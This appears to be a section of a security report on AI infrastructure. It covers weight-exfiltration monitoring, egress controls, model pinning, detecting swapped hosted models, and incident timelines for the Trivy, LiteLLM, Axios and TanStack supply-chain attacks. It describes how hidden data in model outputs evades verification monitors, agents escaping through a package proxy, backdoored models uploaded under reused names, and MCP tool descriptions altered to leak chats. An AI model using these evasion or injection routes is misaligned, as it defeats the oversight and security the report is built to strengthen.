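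Brown and colleagues compressed a model with 1.5 billion parameters to 1.15 bits per parameter. After further training, it scored only 1.6% lower on a standard knowledge test. They describe this as 16-fold compression, although going from 16 bits to 1.15 is closer to 14-fold. Their upper figure of 100-fold is more speculative because it is based on how closely a larger model's compressed weights matched the originals, and a close match does not guarantee that the model still works well.

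A defender can also look for the hidden data. *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration* (Rinberg, Karvonen and colleagues, 2025) proposes repeating each request on a trusted server with the same random seed, the number that determines the model's random choices. The two servers should produce the same tokens, the units of text that a model writes. An attacker has to change some of these tokens to hide data. Rinberg and colleagues estimate that this check would extend the theft of a 1 TB model from about one day to more than 200 days. They give the false-positive rate as below 1% in their summary and as 0.01% elsewhere, a large difference for a service that handles millions of requests.

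Rounding differences between machines also change tokens. In *Anytime-valid detection of LLM weight exfiltration*, Ortega-Fernandez, Kowalczyk and Warr (2026) found that between 41% and 87% of normal responses contained at least one mismatch, depending on the model. They also tested an alarm that goes off at the first token Rinberg and colleagues' rule classes as dangerous. It went off in 98% to 100% of normal streams of 250 responses. The comparison is somewhat harsh on Rinberg and colleagues, who had not specified how to combine evidence over time.

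Ortega-Fernandez and colleagues combine it with a running score. For each response, let A be 1 if the response contains a mismatch that rounding is unlikely to explain, and 0 otherwise. Let q be a cautious estimate of how often A is 1 in normal traffic. The score starts at 1, and each response multiplies it by

1 + λ(A − q),

where λ, set from earlier responses, controls how strongly the score reacts. With q = 0.1 and λ = 2, a suspicious response multiplies the score by 2.8 and an ordinary one by 0.8. In normal traffic the average factor is 0.1 × 2.8 + 0.9 × 0.8 = 1, so the score has no tendency to grow. The full method averages seven such scores, each with a different threshold for a suspicious mismatch, and raises an alarm at 200. This keeps the probability of ever raising a false alarm below 1%, however long the monitoring lasts, provided that the requests, model and serving software stay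 like those used for calibration.

When the attacker did not know the random seed, the score detected the attack in every test stream, after a median of 6 to 14 responses, and raised no false alarms. These streams resampled a limited set of recorded responses, so real traffic would probably be more varied. An attacker who knew the seed could choose changes that looked like rounding errors. On one of the four models, the score did not detect this attacker within 250 responses, even at the highest tested rate of 0.0304 bits per token. At that rate, leaking 140 GB would take about 37 trillion tokens, but leaking a 256-bit key would take only about 8,400.

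### What AI developers say about their controls

Anthropic's *Activating AI Safety Level 3 Protections* (2025) describes limits on how fast data can leave the environments that hold model weights. The company calls these controls "preliminary" and more experimental than its other measures. *Activating ASL3 protections*, a shorter Anthropic announcement, says that unusual bandwidth use can trigger a block. The company expects the limits to become low enough "over time" that stealing a model without detection would be very difficult.

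OpenAI's *Securing research infrastructure for advanced AI* describes a policy of denying outbound traffic by default and listing the permitted routes. Maginative's *OpenAI Shares Insights on How It's Securing AI Research Infrastructure* mentions further, undisclosed detection controls around unreleased weights. SiliconANGLE (2025) later reported that OpenAI had also disconnected some of its systems from outside networks.

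There is much less public evidence of what such controls achieve. Anthropic reports one benefit, that setting the limits forced it to learn how data leaves its systems, but it does not publish the limits or say how reliably they would detect a theft. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that in July 2026, AI agents under evaluation at the company reached the internet through an internal package proxy that was allowed to download packages, and that an alert about unusual credential use led to the discovery. A package proxy therefore needs its own egress allowlist and monitoring.

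OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) announced stricter network isolation after the incident. OpenAI designed the new controls so that compromising one job or supporting service would not be enough to reach the internet, but it gave no test results with the announcement. It also said that it was still improving how it collects and monitors security logs.

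### Linking a connection to a process and package

A network alert usually identifies a machine, but several jobs may share that machine. To find the process responsible, the team can match the alert with the machine's records. The operating system gives each outgoing connection a temporary port number, and an eBPF monitor can record that number with the process ID. Suppose the firewall logs a connection from port 51544 on a training machine to an unfamiliar address at 14:02:07. If the machine's records show process 8123 using that port for the same destination at that moment, process 8123 made the connection. The times need to match because the operating system reuses port numbers.

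Containers and proxies make it harder to match a connection to the process that opened it. Containers often share their machine's address, and the machine may rewrite their port numbers as traffic leaves, so the team also needs a record of those changes. A proxy opens a second connection on the client's behalf, so the team must find the request in the proxy's log before it can look for the process.

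Identifying the package is harder still. In *DySec*'s tests, eBPF probes recorded the remote address, port and state of each connection while one package was installing, so a connection to an unusual port, such as 6667, was easy to attribute to that package. A training job, however, may load hundreds of packages into a single process, and the kernel does not record which of them opened a connection. Python's audit events include connection attempts, so a recorder that starts early enough can note which code made the attempt and look for its file in the lists of installed files that pip keeps for each package. The second-stage script has no file of its own, so the recorder would probably find only unnamed code launched during Python's startup. That would still be a good reason to check for startup hooks.

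Without these links, the team in the example would know that one of its machines had contacted an unfamiliar server, but not which job's keys to replace or which package to remove. It would also need looser rules. A rule that can't distinguish Git from a training job must let both contact a code host, even if only Git has a reason to.

Tan and colleagues found such links difficult to recover even in a controlled setting. Their software could not trace any of eight transitions between attack steps through a continuous chain of records. In four of them, the steps were close enough in time for a link to be plausible, and the other four had longer gaps. They list better attribution of network traffic to processes as future work.

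### Permitted hosts and missing downloads

Allowlists work poorly when attackers use the same services as developers. Unit 42's *Connecting the Dots* describes ChainDrop, an npm worm that infected more than 400 packages. The worm downloaded the Bun runtime and used stolen tokens to create code repositories. If a build machine is allowed to reach GitHub, its lookups, connection records and server names look much the same whether it is fetching the team's code or sending data to an attacker's repository. Full inspection can show which repository and account a program used, and a proxy can allow only the approved ones.

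ChainDrop also managed its control servers through transactions on the Ethereum blockchain. A list of known malicious addresses soon goes out of date against such malware because the attacker can publish a new address at any time. An allowlist would still block the new address unless it belonged to a permitted service. Despite these limits, Unit 42 recommends restricting outbound traffic from build systems.

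Small thefts are also hard to detect from traffic volume. The job in the example regularly sends sample outputs to the grader, perhaps several megabytes at a time. If malware could send a few kilobytes of keys through the same provider, the extra traffic would fall within the normal variation. Encryption would hide the contents from every sensor except full inspection, and the malware could hide the keys from that too by encrypting them before sending.

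Finally, software can enter an environment without a new package download. If pip has a copy in its local cache, it may request the package's index page but not the file, so the proxy records the name without the version. A container image can arrive with hundreds of packages already installed, but the network log shows only the image's download. A laboratory may also copy packages between machines on shared storage, bypassing the registry proxy. The proxy's log is therefore an incomplete record of installed software, and the team still needs an inventory of each environment.

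## How can a change on a remote server be detected?

A job can behave differently from one day to the next even though its own files and network destinations stay the same. Its code may request something by name, such as the newest version of a model, and somebody else decides what that name currently refers to. The team can detect a change in a remote file by hashing it, but with a hosted model they can only test the answers.

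### Mutable references

A mutable reference is a name that its owner can point to new content. A Git branch moves with every new commit, and a container image's "latest" tag usually points to the newest build. Owners can often move tags that look like version numbers, too. Build pipelines use such tags, as one of OpenAI's workflows did.

On Hugging Face, the usual command for loading a model gives only the author and the model's name, so it fetches the latest version. A second setting can fix the version:

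```
from_pretrained("Author/ModelName")
from_pretrained("Author/ModelName", revision="<commit identifier>")
```

A commit identifier is a hash of the repository's contents and history, so changing the contents changes the identifier. The revision setting also accepts a branch or tag name, but these can later point to a different commit.

The scripts that some models run while loading can change in the same way. *An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution* (2026) counted around 45,000 repositories with such scripts on five platforms. Pinning a model does not always pin its scripts, because the model's settings can refer to a script in another repository. The Transformers library has a separate setting for that script's revision, which defaults to the main branch.

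### Reused model names

An account name can also pass to a new owner. *Model Namespace Reuse* (Saraf and Balassiano, 2025) showed that anyone could register the name of a deleted Hugging Face account. The new owner could then upload a different model under the old name, and any program that loaded the model by name would receive the replacement.

Users may notice a deleted account because their downloads fail with error 404 until somebody registers the name again. They get no such warning if the owner transferred the model to another account before deleting the old one, because Hugging Face redirects requests to the new location (status code 307) and downloads keep working. If an attacker then registers the old name and uploads a model there, the redirect stops and the same request returns the attacker's model.

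Saraf and Balassiano of Unit 42 tested this on two cloud platforms. They found models in the catalogues of Google's Vertex AI and Microsoft's Azure AI Foundry whose authors' accounts no longer existed on Hugging Face. For each platform, they registered an abandoned name, uploaded a model containing a backdoor, deployed it and gained access to the machine that ran it. They also found reusable names in thousands of open-source projects. The article reports no criminal use of the method.

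After a report in February 2025, Google began scanning daily for models with missing authors and blocking deployment of those models. Such a scan has to find the model before an attacker takes the author's name, because after that the author no longer appears to be missing.

### Pinning and recording

To pin downloadable content, a team resolves the name once and then stops relying on it:

1. Ask the server which commit or image hash the name refers to now.
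2. Download that exact version, hash every file and review the contents.
3. Add the identifier and the file hashes to the approved set.
4. In later jobs, request the identifier instead of the name, and compare the files received with the recorded hashes.

Pinning downloads to an approved commit would have blocked attacks that reused repository names. An attacker's new repository does not contain the pinned commit, so the download fails. If the attacker uploaded a copy of the original history, the download would return the original files.

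A pinned job doesn't detect when the name starts pointing somewhere else. A small scheduled program can resolve the name daily and report a new commit or a redirect to another owner, without installing anything. Saraf and Balassiano also recommend keeping copies of important models in trusted storage, so the job can still run if the original disappears.

Some content, such as a script or dataset at an ordinary web address, has no identifier to pin. A recording proxy can help detect changes to this content. It passes on each request, stores the response with its time, address and hash, and compares it with earlier responses to the same request. If a script changes, the team can compare the old and new versions line by line. The proxy records what the job itself received, whereas a malicious server could send a harmless file to a separate scanner. Pages that include the current time or a random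 number differ on every request, so the proxy must ignore those parts to avoid constant false alarms.

| Method | What it catches | What it misses | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pinning to a hash | Any change to the pinned files | Anything those files download later | Someone must approve every update, including security fixes |
| Resolving the name again each day | A moved branch or tag, or a new owner | A change reversed between checks | One small request per name |
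| Keeping a local copy | Nothing by itself, but it keeps upstream changes out of the job | Flaws already in the copy | Storage, such as 140 GB for each version of the example's base model |
| Recording proxy | Any difference between responses to the same request | A server-side change that leaves the response the same | Storage, and protecting the decrypted traffic |

In the running example, the job might send 50,000 samples a day to the grader. At 4 kB per request-response pair, the recordings would take up 200 MB a day, or 73 GB a year. Comparing their hashes would be of little use, because a language model can answer the same question in different words each time. The recordings are still useful as samples for the statistical tests described below.

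### Tool servers that change after approval

Many AI agents use outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting language models to other software. A tool server sends the agent each tool's name, its input format and a description in ordinary language. The description usually goes into the model's prompt, so whoever controls the server can change the agent's behaviour by editing it.

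Security researchers call a malicious change to a tool after approval a "rug pull". *ETDI* (2025) explains that standard clients typically approve a tool once and don't recheck its full definition before later calls. *MCP-38* (2026) finds that current clients don't alert users when a definition changes. *MCPGuard* (2025) describes a tool called get_fact_of_the_day that kept supplying trivia while sending the user's chat history to an attacker's phone number. The paper calls this a real-world example, but it seems to have been a demonstration by the security company Invariant Labs.

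A client could hash each tool's definition at approval and ask the user to approve it again if the hash changes. It should first put the fields in a fixed order, so that harmless reordering does not cause an alarm. Hashing would catch a changed description, but not changed code behind the same description or a malicious update to one of the server's dependencies. *MCP-38* also warns of gradual drift, in which many small edits together make a tool malicious. Each edit would change the hash, but a reviewer who looked only at the latest edit might accept them all. It is safer to show the reviewer the text the team originally approved.

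### Hosted models behind a stable name

Providers of hosted models sometimes announce that an existing model name will refer to a different model. Cloudflare announced in *Planned model deprecations on Workers AI* (2026) that requests for Kimi K2.5 would go to Kimi K2.6, at a higher price, from 30 May 2026. Together AI redirects requests for Mistral-7B-Instruct-v0.3 to the newer Ministral-3-14B. For replacements that behave very differently or change the price by more than 10%, its policy is to give two weeks' notice and require customers to switch models themselves.

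When a provider redirects requests to a different model, a job that does not check the provider's announcements may continue without an error. The cloud platform Heroku (2026) instead adds a warning to responses from models it plans to retire, and later returns error 410 for requests to them. A team can automatically record such warnings and any model name that the provider includes in its responses.

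Neither record helps with a change that the provider has not noticed. Anthropic's *A postmortem of three recent issues* describes three bugs that intermittently made Claude's answers worse. According to InfoQ (2025), they arose in the service's infrastructure, request routing and compilation in August and early September 2025. At the peak, they affected 16% of requests to Claude Sonnet 4 (Chauvin, Lalanne et al., *Token-Efficient Change Detection in LLM APIs*, 2026).

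### Comparing answers statistically

A caller can compare a hosted model's answers with reference answers. For an open model, these can come from a copy that the caller runs from the published weights. For a closed model, they can be the service's own earlier answers, but the comparison then reveals only changes made after those answers were collected.

An early method of this kind comes from Gao, Liang and Guestrin (2024), in *Model Equality Testing*. They collected about ten answers to each of 25 prompts from both the reference and the service. They measured the similarity of two answers to the same prompt by counting the positions at which both have the same character. Leaving out a scaling factor, the distance between the two sets is

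D = (average similarity within the reference) + (average similarity within the service) − 2 × (average similarity between them).

Suppose two reference answers match at 30 positions on average, two service answers match at 34, and a reference answer and a service answer match at 26. Then D = 30 + 34 − 2 × 26 = 12. If both sets of answers came from the same model, all three averages would be about equal and D would be close to 0.

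Chance alone can also produce a positive distance. To find out how often, the tester mixes the two sets of answers to each prompt, divides them at random into two new groups and calculates D again. If 8 of 1,000 such shuffles give a distance of 12 or more, the p-value is 0.8%. A tester who accepts a 1% false-alarm rate would conclude that the models differ.

In simulations with a 5% false-alarm rate, the method detected a median of 77.4% of changes from quantization (storing weights with fewer bits) or watermarking. Gao and colleagues then tested 31 commercial endpoints (each a single model offered by one provider) for Llama models in summer 2024. Eleven gave answers that differed from those of Meta's published weights, and each audit cost less than $1. Quantization or a faulty sampling setting could also explain a difference, so the result does not imply that the providers had secretly substituted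 another model.

### Cheaper and more sensitive tests

Testing one model hourly with this method would cost about $146 a year at GPT-4.1 prices, according to *Log Probability Tracking of LLM APIs* (Chauvin, Le Merrer and colleagues, 2025). The paper's own method, which would cost $0.14 a year, sends the letter "x" and asks for one token of output and the log probabilities of the most likely tokens. These log probabilities vary slightly even when the model stays the same, so the test compares their averages over many requests.

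On 290 slightly altered models, log-probability tracking scored 0.915 and Model Equality Testing scored 0.670. The score is the probability that a changed model looks more different from the original than an unchanged one does, so guessing would score 0.5. Chauvin and colleagues also monitored 189 endpoints for more than four months and found 37 suspected changes, but they had no independent record of when the models changed. Two providers replied that they could not discuss the details, although one said that it made changes regularly. Log-probability tracking is unavailable for most services, because only 23% of the reachable endpoints on the gateway OpenRouter returned log probabilities.

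A later method, B3IT, needs only the text of a model's answers. It looks for prompts where two tokens are almost equally likely to come first in the answer, and sets the temperature, which controls the randomness of the answers, to zero. At this setting, a model normally gives the same first token every time, but when two tokens are almost equally likely, tiny numerical differences can lead to either one. Even a slight change to the model's weights may favour one token enough that the other stops appearing.

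Suppose a prompt originally produced "yes" and "no" equally often. If the model has not changed, three new samples will all be the same with probability 2 × (1/2)³ = 25%, so treating identical answers as evidence of a change would cause too many false alarms. With ten samples, the probability falls to about 0.2%. Chauvin and colleagues take only three samples per prompt but average the results over five prompts. In their benchmark, B3IT scored 0.90 at a cost of $2.20 a year for hourly tests, compared with 0.88 at $67 for a zero-temperature version of Model Equality Testing.

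B3IT detected lasting changes in 8 of 53 commercial endpoints over 23 days. One of these changes matched Together AI's redirect of Mistral-7B-Instruct-v0.3, but the others had no direct confirmation. In a wider search, 78% of 131 endpoints had at least one prompt suitable for the method.

These tests work less well if a provider sends only some requests to a cheaper model. *API-TAIL* (Mei, Tian and colleagues, 2026) tests for this by running the advertised model separately and measuring how improbable each answer is under that model. Honest providers often use different sampling settings, which make the whole batch of answers more or less improbable. API-TAIL therefore adjusts the temperature to fit the batch, then counts the answers that are still very improbable.

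API-TAIL detected substitution at least 69% of the time in 13 of 16 test settings when 10% of 200 requests went to a substitute. It wrongly flagged endpoints with no substitution and ordinary settings in at most 6.9% of audits. Adapted versions of two earlier tests, including Model Equality Testing, detected none of the main substitutions on short answers. API-TAIL has trouble detecting substitutions between closely related models. When the substitute was the previous release of the same model, served by its developer, API-TAIL detected it at most 7% of the time on long answers, even when a quarter of 400 requests went to it.

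The same study illustrates how hard it is to define an honest service. One provider openly adds its own system prompt (standing instructions to the model), and API-TAIL flagged that provider in 79% of audits with short answers and 99% with long ones. This is a false alarm for someone looking for fraud, but a team that approved the model without the extra prompt would probably find the warning useful.

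### Testing the replaced grader

The team in the running example has no copy of the grader's weights, so it cannot use API-TAIL. Instead, it can use the grader's earlier scores as the reference. At approval, the team chooses 100 sample outputs, has the grader score each one many times on a scale from 0 to 10, and records the averages. After that, the grader scores the same 100 outputs once a day.

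Suppose repeated scores for the same output have a standard deviation of 1 point. The average of 100 scores then has a standard error of 1/√100 = 0.1 points. The new grader gives scores that are 0.3 points higher on average. The team raises an alarm if the daily average differs from the reference by more than a chosen threshold. With a normal approximation, the error rates are:

| Test outputs | Threshold | False alarms per test | Changes missed per test |
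|---|---|---|---|
| 100 | 0.20 | 4.6% | 16% |
| 100 | 0.30 | 0.3% | 50% |
| 400 | 0.15 | 0.3% | 0.1% |

With 100 outputs and a threshold of 0.20, the team would get about 17 false alarms a year. Raising the threshold to 0.30 would reduce this to about one, but the test would then miss the new grader half the time. Using 400 outputs makes both errors rare because it halves the standard error. The team also gets another chance each day to detect a lasting change.

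The average score can hide a change that raises some scores and lowers others. The team should therefore also compare the scores for each output, or run a test like B3IT if the service allows it. B3IT could detect smaller changes to the grader, but it would not show whether the new grader was more lenient.

After an alarm, the team can't get the old grader back, but it can use the new one to rescore every candidate version of its own model so that all the scores are comparable. The earlier decisions that need checking are probably those made since the last passed test, though the team should go back a few days further if the test often misses changes.

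### What these tests cannot show

Random test requests will usually miss a change that affects only rare inputs. If the change affects a fraction f of ordinary requests, the probability that N random test requests all miss it is (1 − f)^N. For a change that affects one request in 10,000, 200 tests miss it 98% of the time. The team would need about 30,000 tests for a 95% chance of including at least one affected request, and would detect the change only if the answer to that request looked different. A backdoor that responds only to a secret phrase could go undetected through any practical number of tests.

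A dishonest provider could also recognise the test prompts and send them to the original model, so *Auditing Black-Box LLM APIs with a Rank-Based Uniformity Test* (2025) recommends prompts that look like ordinary traffic. The single letter "x" and a set of 100 outputs that arrives every morning are both easy to recognise. The team could mix its test outputs into the job's normal requests and regularly replace some of the test outputs, although each replacement needs new reference scores.

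New hardware, a different system prompt or a new model can each alter the answers, so a failed test does not identify the cause. A passed test does not prove that the model is the right one. *Real Money, Fake Models* (2026), which applied Model Equality Testing to resold access to commercial models, cautions that a pass shows only that the test found no difference in the samples collected.

Stronger evidence requires the provider's cooperation. A provider can, in principle, attach a cryptographic proof that a particular model produced an answer. But Chauvin and colleagues report that one such system takes several minutes to generate a proof for a model with 13 billion parameters. That is too slow for a grader that handles thousands of samples a day.

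## How were real attacks on AI software noticed?

The victim's own monitoring is seldom credited with discovering the best-documented attacks on AI software. Several were noticed because a computer slowed down or an outside researcher contacted the victim. The affected projects and companies have described in detail what the attackers left behind, but they often don't say clearly what first made anyone suspicious.

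### Three earlier cases

In December 2022, somebody uploaded a malicious package to PyPI under the same name as a dependency of PyTorch's nightly builds, the daily test versions of the framework. PyTorch kept the real dependency on its own server, but pip installed the copy on PyPI instead. Linux users who installed a nightly build with pip between 25 and 30 December could receive the malicious package. It collected system details and private files, including login keys, and sent them out through domain-name lookups. PyTorch said it learned of the package on 30 December but did not explain how.

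The malicious versions of the Ultralytics package in December 2024 mined cryptocurrency, which takes a lot of processing power. Users complained of overloaded processors, and a comparison showed that the published package differed from the project's source code. The first malicious version was available for about twelve hours.

In March 2025, attackers compromised tj-actions/changed-files, a build step that lists a project's changed files. They moved its version tags to point to malicious code, which printed each pipeline's credentials in its build log. Anyone could read the logs of public projects. The security company StepSecurity reported that its network monitor had flagged a connection to an unexpected destination during builds. More than 20,000 projects used the step, and the malicious code was available for about a day.

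### Trivy, a security scanner

BoostSecurity's *20 Days Later* points out that attackers moved version tags again almost exactly a year later, this time those of a security tool, Trivy. This open-source program from Aqua Security searches code and container images for known vulnerabilities. Many projects run it automatically in their build pipelines through two reusable steps, trivy-action and setup-trivy. A scanner makes a good target because it runs in the same environment as the pipeline's credentials and is expected to read many files. An attacker who controls it can also reach every project that uses it.

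Aqua Security's *Ongoing Investigation and Continued Remediation* (2026) traces the attack to late February, when attackers exploited a misconfiguration in Trivy's build environment and stole a privileged access token. The Trivy team disclosed the incident on 1 March and replaced its credentials, but missed some. On 19 March the attackers used their remaining access to publish a malicious Trivy release, version 0.69.4. They also redirected 76 of the 77 tags of trivy-action, and all seven of setup-trivy, to code that stole credentials.

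Aqua gives these exposure windows:

| Component | Dangerous from (UTC) | Until (UTC) | Duration |
|---|---|---|---|
| trivy-action | 19 March, 17:43 | 20 March, 05:40 | 11 h 57 min |
| setup-trivy | 19 March, 17:43 | 19 March, 21:44 | 4 h 1 min |
| Trivy 0.69.4 | 19 March, 18:22 | 19 March, 21:42 | 3 h 20 min |

Kurmi reports about the same durations. Aqua also states that the Trivy team identified and contained the attack at about 20:38, nearly three hours after it began. However, trivy-action remained dangerous for another nine hours, according to Aqua's own figures.

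Users of the two steps had little reason to suspect anything. The malicious code ran first and the real scan followed, so the pipeline finished with its usual output. GitHub even displayed an "Immutable" badge beside the altered tags. But the attack did leave traces:

| Where | Trace |
|---|---|
| Git history | New commits without the originals' signatures, which claimed to be years old but followed a commit from March 2026 |
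| Processes | A script reading the memory of the program that runs build jobs |
| Network traffic | An upload to a misspelt version of Aqua's domain |
| The victim's GitHub account | In some cases, a new public repository holding the stolen data |
| Developers' own machines | A new script and a background service to run it |

Anyone could see the Git traces because the repositories are public. A pipeline that requested the build step by its commit hash would not have run the malicious code.

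Aqua does not say what alerted the Trivy team. CrowdStrike's *From Scanner to Stealer* reports that the security company's engineers traced a spike in alerts about running scripts, across several customers, to trivy-action. Process monitoring gave a useful alarm in this case, although it is unclear whether CrowdStrike or the Trivy team noticed the attack first. Microsoft (2026) reports that its cloud security product observed the whole attack on build machines that organisations ran themselves. That is weaker evidence of early warning, because a product can record every step before anyone realises that the steps belong to an attack.

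According to InfoQ (2026), the attackers also tried to delay countermeasures by deleting earlier discussions of the incident and flooding others with spam. They returned on 22 March, publishing two more malicious container images in the afternoon and making some of Aqua's internal repositories public in the evening. Aqua's team discovered unauthorised changes to its repositories while the company was bringing in an incident response firm.

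Aqua found no sign that the attack had affected its commercial products, which it builds separately. It advised everyone who had run the malicious code to treat any credentials the code could have accessed as stolen. In its review, the Trivy project called its initial response inefficient and announced new monitoring of its release pipeline to notice unexpected changes sooner.

### LiteLLM 1.82.7 and 1.82.8

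LiteLLM was one of the projects that ran Trivy in its pipeline. On 24 March, five days after the attack on Trivy, attackers uploaded two malicious versions of LiteLLM directly to PyPI. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) gives the compromised scanner as the suspected cause. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) more firmly attributes the releases to an API token that leaked through Trivy.

The discovery began when an engineer at FutureSearch, a company that builds AI research tools, noticed a laptop slow almost to a halt. FutureSearch's *How a Poisoned litellm Package Compromised an MCP Server in Cursor* reports that the processor was fully occupied, 11,000 processes were running, and the code editor Cursor had requested network access just as the machine froze. The malware had caused this by mistake. Version 1.82.8 of litellm contained a startup hook that launched a new Python process, which ran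 the same hook and launched another, until the processes overwhelmed the machine.

Cursor had started a local MCP tool server, and the program that launched the server automatically downloaded the newest permitted version of each dependency, including LiteLLM, which the engineer had not chosen to install that day. The engineer's project had an older version of LiteLLM and a version limit that excluded the malicious ones, so inspecting the project's own dependencies would have revealed nothing wrong.

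FutureSearch's *Catching the LiteLLM PyPI Attack* includes a timeline and the full record of the investigation. Combined with the upload time of version 1.82.7 and PyPI's figures, it gives the following sequence:

| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 10:39 | Attackers upload version 1.82.7 |
| 10:52 | They upload version 1.82.8 |
| 10:58 | The tool server on the laptop downloads 1.82.8 |
| 11:07 | The malware tries to install a file that would let it survive a restart |
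| 11:09 | The engineer forces the laptop to shut down |
| 11:13 | The investigation begins |
| 11:40 | The engineer finds the startup hook |
| 11:58 | The engineer confirms that PyPI is still supplying the file and emails its security team |
| 12:02 | FutureSearch publishes a warning |
| About 13:11 | PyPI quarantines the project |

The right diagnosis came more than half an hour after the slowdown. The engineer asked the coding agent Claude Code to investigate, but its first explanations were wrong. It took the strange Python commands for a normal part of its own operation, reported "no malicious indicators", and later blamed an update to Cursor. The forced shutdown had also destroyed some of the evidence. The engineer remained sceptical and had photographed the process list before switching off. A search of the disk for the first few characters of a command in that photograph led to the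 startup hook in the package cache.

Two further checks showed that the problem came from PyPI rather than the laptop. A fresh download in an isolated container included the same file, and LiteLLM's GitHub repository had no tag for version 1.82.8. A program that compared PyPI releases with GitHub tags could have detected the missing tag within minutes of the upload, though it would also flag projects that publish before tagging.

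Cleaning up was also awkward, because the malicious package came back when the engineer later reopened Cursor and the editor launched the same tool server.

The other malicious version, 1.82.7, lacked the startup hook. Its code ran only when a program loaded LiteLLM's proxy server, so it did not crash machines the way 1.82.8 did. The attackers had uploaded it 13 minutes before 1.82.8, but FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) initially named only 1.82.8 and added 1.82.7 at 12:30. People seem to have found 1.82.7 because the crashes caused by 1.82.8 had led them to investigate. The engineer cites the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy's view that the attack would have gone unnoticed for much longer without the bug.

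The malware also left traces in network traffic when it uploaded data to two domains that did not belong to LiteLLM. It tried to create containers with full privileges on any Kubernetes cluster it could reach, so administrators could look for those. FutureSearch found none on its cluster.

### How long were the LiteLLM releases available?

Published exposure windows for this attack differ by a factor of more than three. LiteLLM puts the window at about 40 minutes. FutureSearch's *LiteLLM Hack* gives 46 minutes, with a quarantine at 11:25. PyPI gives 2 hours 32 minutes, including 1 hour 19 minutes before the first report.

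PyPI's figures are almost certainly the right ones. The first upload was at 10:39, and 1 hour and 19 minutes later is 11:58, the minute the engineer emailed PyPI. The engineer had also just downloaded the malicious file, which would have been impossible if it had been quarantined at 11:25.

The difference matters when checking old build logs. LiteLLM's notice includes scripts contributed by users that search for jobs that installed either version. Their default search ends at 12:44, so a team that changed only the date would miss any job that started in the last 27 minutes before the quarantine. The notice's written advice to check everything up to 16:00 is safer.

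PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads of the malicious versions over 152 minutes, or about 780 a minute. LiteLLM normally has roughly 1,700 installations a minute, so around 46% of installations accepted whichever version was newest. FutureSearch surveyed the 2,337 PyPI packages that depend directly on LiteLLM and found that 2,054 of them (88%) allowed at least one of the malicious versions.

But downloads are a poor measure of harm. Some come from mirrors that copy packages without running them, and one machine may download a package many times. FutureSearch counted 23,142 pip downloads of version 1.82.8 and treats them all as infected environments, arguing that the hook ran during installation. That is doubtful, because pip is already running when it installs the hook. The hook would normally run the next time Python started, which on a build machine might be seconds later or never.

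People who received the malware had to assume it had taken their login keys, cloud credentials and passwords. FutureSearch reported minimal damage and no leak of user data. Users of LiteLLM's official container image were unaffected because that image pins its dependencies. Nobody seems to have published a count of the stolen credentials.

As with Trivy, the attackers tried to suppress the warning. Somebody used the owner's account to close the public GitHub issue about the attack as "not planned", and hundreds of automated accounts filled it with spam. FutureSearch cites an analysis in which Rami McCarthy found a 76% overlap between these accounts and the ones that had flooded the Trivy discussions. The attackers had no control over PyPI's own reporting button, and 13 users reported the project through it.

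Even if PyPI had responded faster, the malicious releases would have stayed available for a long time. In a related attack a few days later on telnyx, another PyPI package, trusted reporters could trigger an automatic quarantine, but the releases were still available for 3 hours and 42 minutes. Nearly half of that time passed before anyone reported them.

### Axios and OpenAI's signing workflow

Axios is a JavaScript library for making web requests, with more than 100 million downloads a week. SecurityWeek's *OpenAI Impacted by North Korea-Linked Axios Supply Chain Hack* reports that in late March 2026 attackers took over a lead maintainer's npm account and published two malicious packages. The packages were available for three hours, according to CPO Magazine, and installed a program that gave the attackers remote control of the infected machine.

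During that time, an automated workflow at OpenAI downloaded and ran one of them. The workflow prepared the company's macOS applications, including ChatGPT Desktop and the coding tool Codex, and had access to the certificate that identifies them as OpenAI's. OpenAI's *Our response to the Axios developer tool compromise* (2026) attributes the incident to a misconfiguration of the workflow, which referred to a component by a movable tag instead of a commit hash and set no minimum age for new packages.

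OpenAI disclosed the incident on 10 April, ten days after the malicious release, but did not say what led it to examine the workflow. The attack on Axios was widely known by then, so the company may have searched its build records for the bad version, or one of its own alarms may have alerted it.

OpenAI concluded that the malware had probably not obtained the certificate, partly because of the order in which the job ran the package and received the certificate. Apple examines macOS applications before release in a process called notarization, and OpenAI found no unexpected applications among those submitted with its credentials. This is fairly strong evidence that nobody had used the stolen certificate, if it was stolen, because malware inside the workflow could not easily have altered Apple's records. But a thief could still have kept the certificate for later, so OpenAI replaced it and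 asked macOS users to update their applications by 8 May.

### TanStack and two OpenAI devices

On 11 May 2026, attackers published 84 malicious versions of 42 packages from TanStack, a family of JavaScript libraries for web applications. InfoQ's *TanStack Details Sophisticated npm Supply Chain Attack That Compromised 42 Packages* (2026) reports that this took six minutes. The attackers planted harmful content in a cache that the project's build pipeline reused, then extracted a short-lived publishing credential from the running pipeline, so they did not need a maintainer's password. GDS K S's *TanStack shipped a postmortem for the 42-package npm compromise* notes that the packages carried valid build attestations.

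The TanStack attack was discovered unusually quickly. A researcher at StepSecurity identified it within 20 minutes, according to traeai's *Postmortem*, which reproduces TanStack's own account. An odd entry in the packages' dependency lists revealed the attack. TanStack learned of it from outside researchers, and none of its own alerts had gone off.

The malicious versions stayed available for much longer than researchers took to find them. According to GDS K S, TanStack took 1 hour and 43 minutes to mark the versions as deprecated, which warns users but does not stop an installation. The files then disappeared from npm over about four and a half hours. Anyone who installed TanStack packages in the meantime could still receive malware that researchers had already identified.

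The malware ran on two employee devices at OpenAI. *Our response to the TanStack npm supply chain attack* (OpenAI, 2026) describes unauthorised access to a few internal code repositories that the two employees could use, and the theft of "limited credential material". The repositories contained certificates for signing OpenAI's applications on several platforms, so OpenAI replaced certificates for the second time in two months. OpenAI found no effect on customer data or production systems and no misuse of the stolen credentials.

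After the Axios incident, OpenAI had begun introducing stricter settings for package installation, including a minimum age for new releases, but the two devices had not yet received them. OpenAI believes the settings would have prevented the download. This is plausible because researchers identified the packages the same day.

OpenAI published its account two days after the attack but, as with Axios, did not describe the first sign. It observed activity that matched the malware's "publicly described behavior". That wording may mean that investigators searched for traces others had already published, or only that they compared their own findings with those descriptions.

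Grafana Labs, which makes monitoring software, also had an intrusion that led to a ransom incident. According to its *Post-incident review for TanStack npm supply chain ransom incident* (2026), the attackers reached only its GitHub environment and did not enter customers' production systems.

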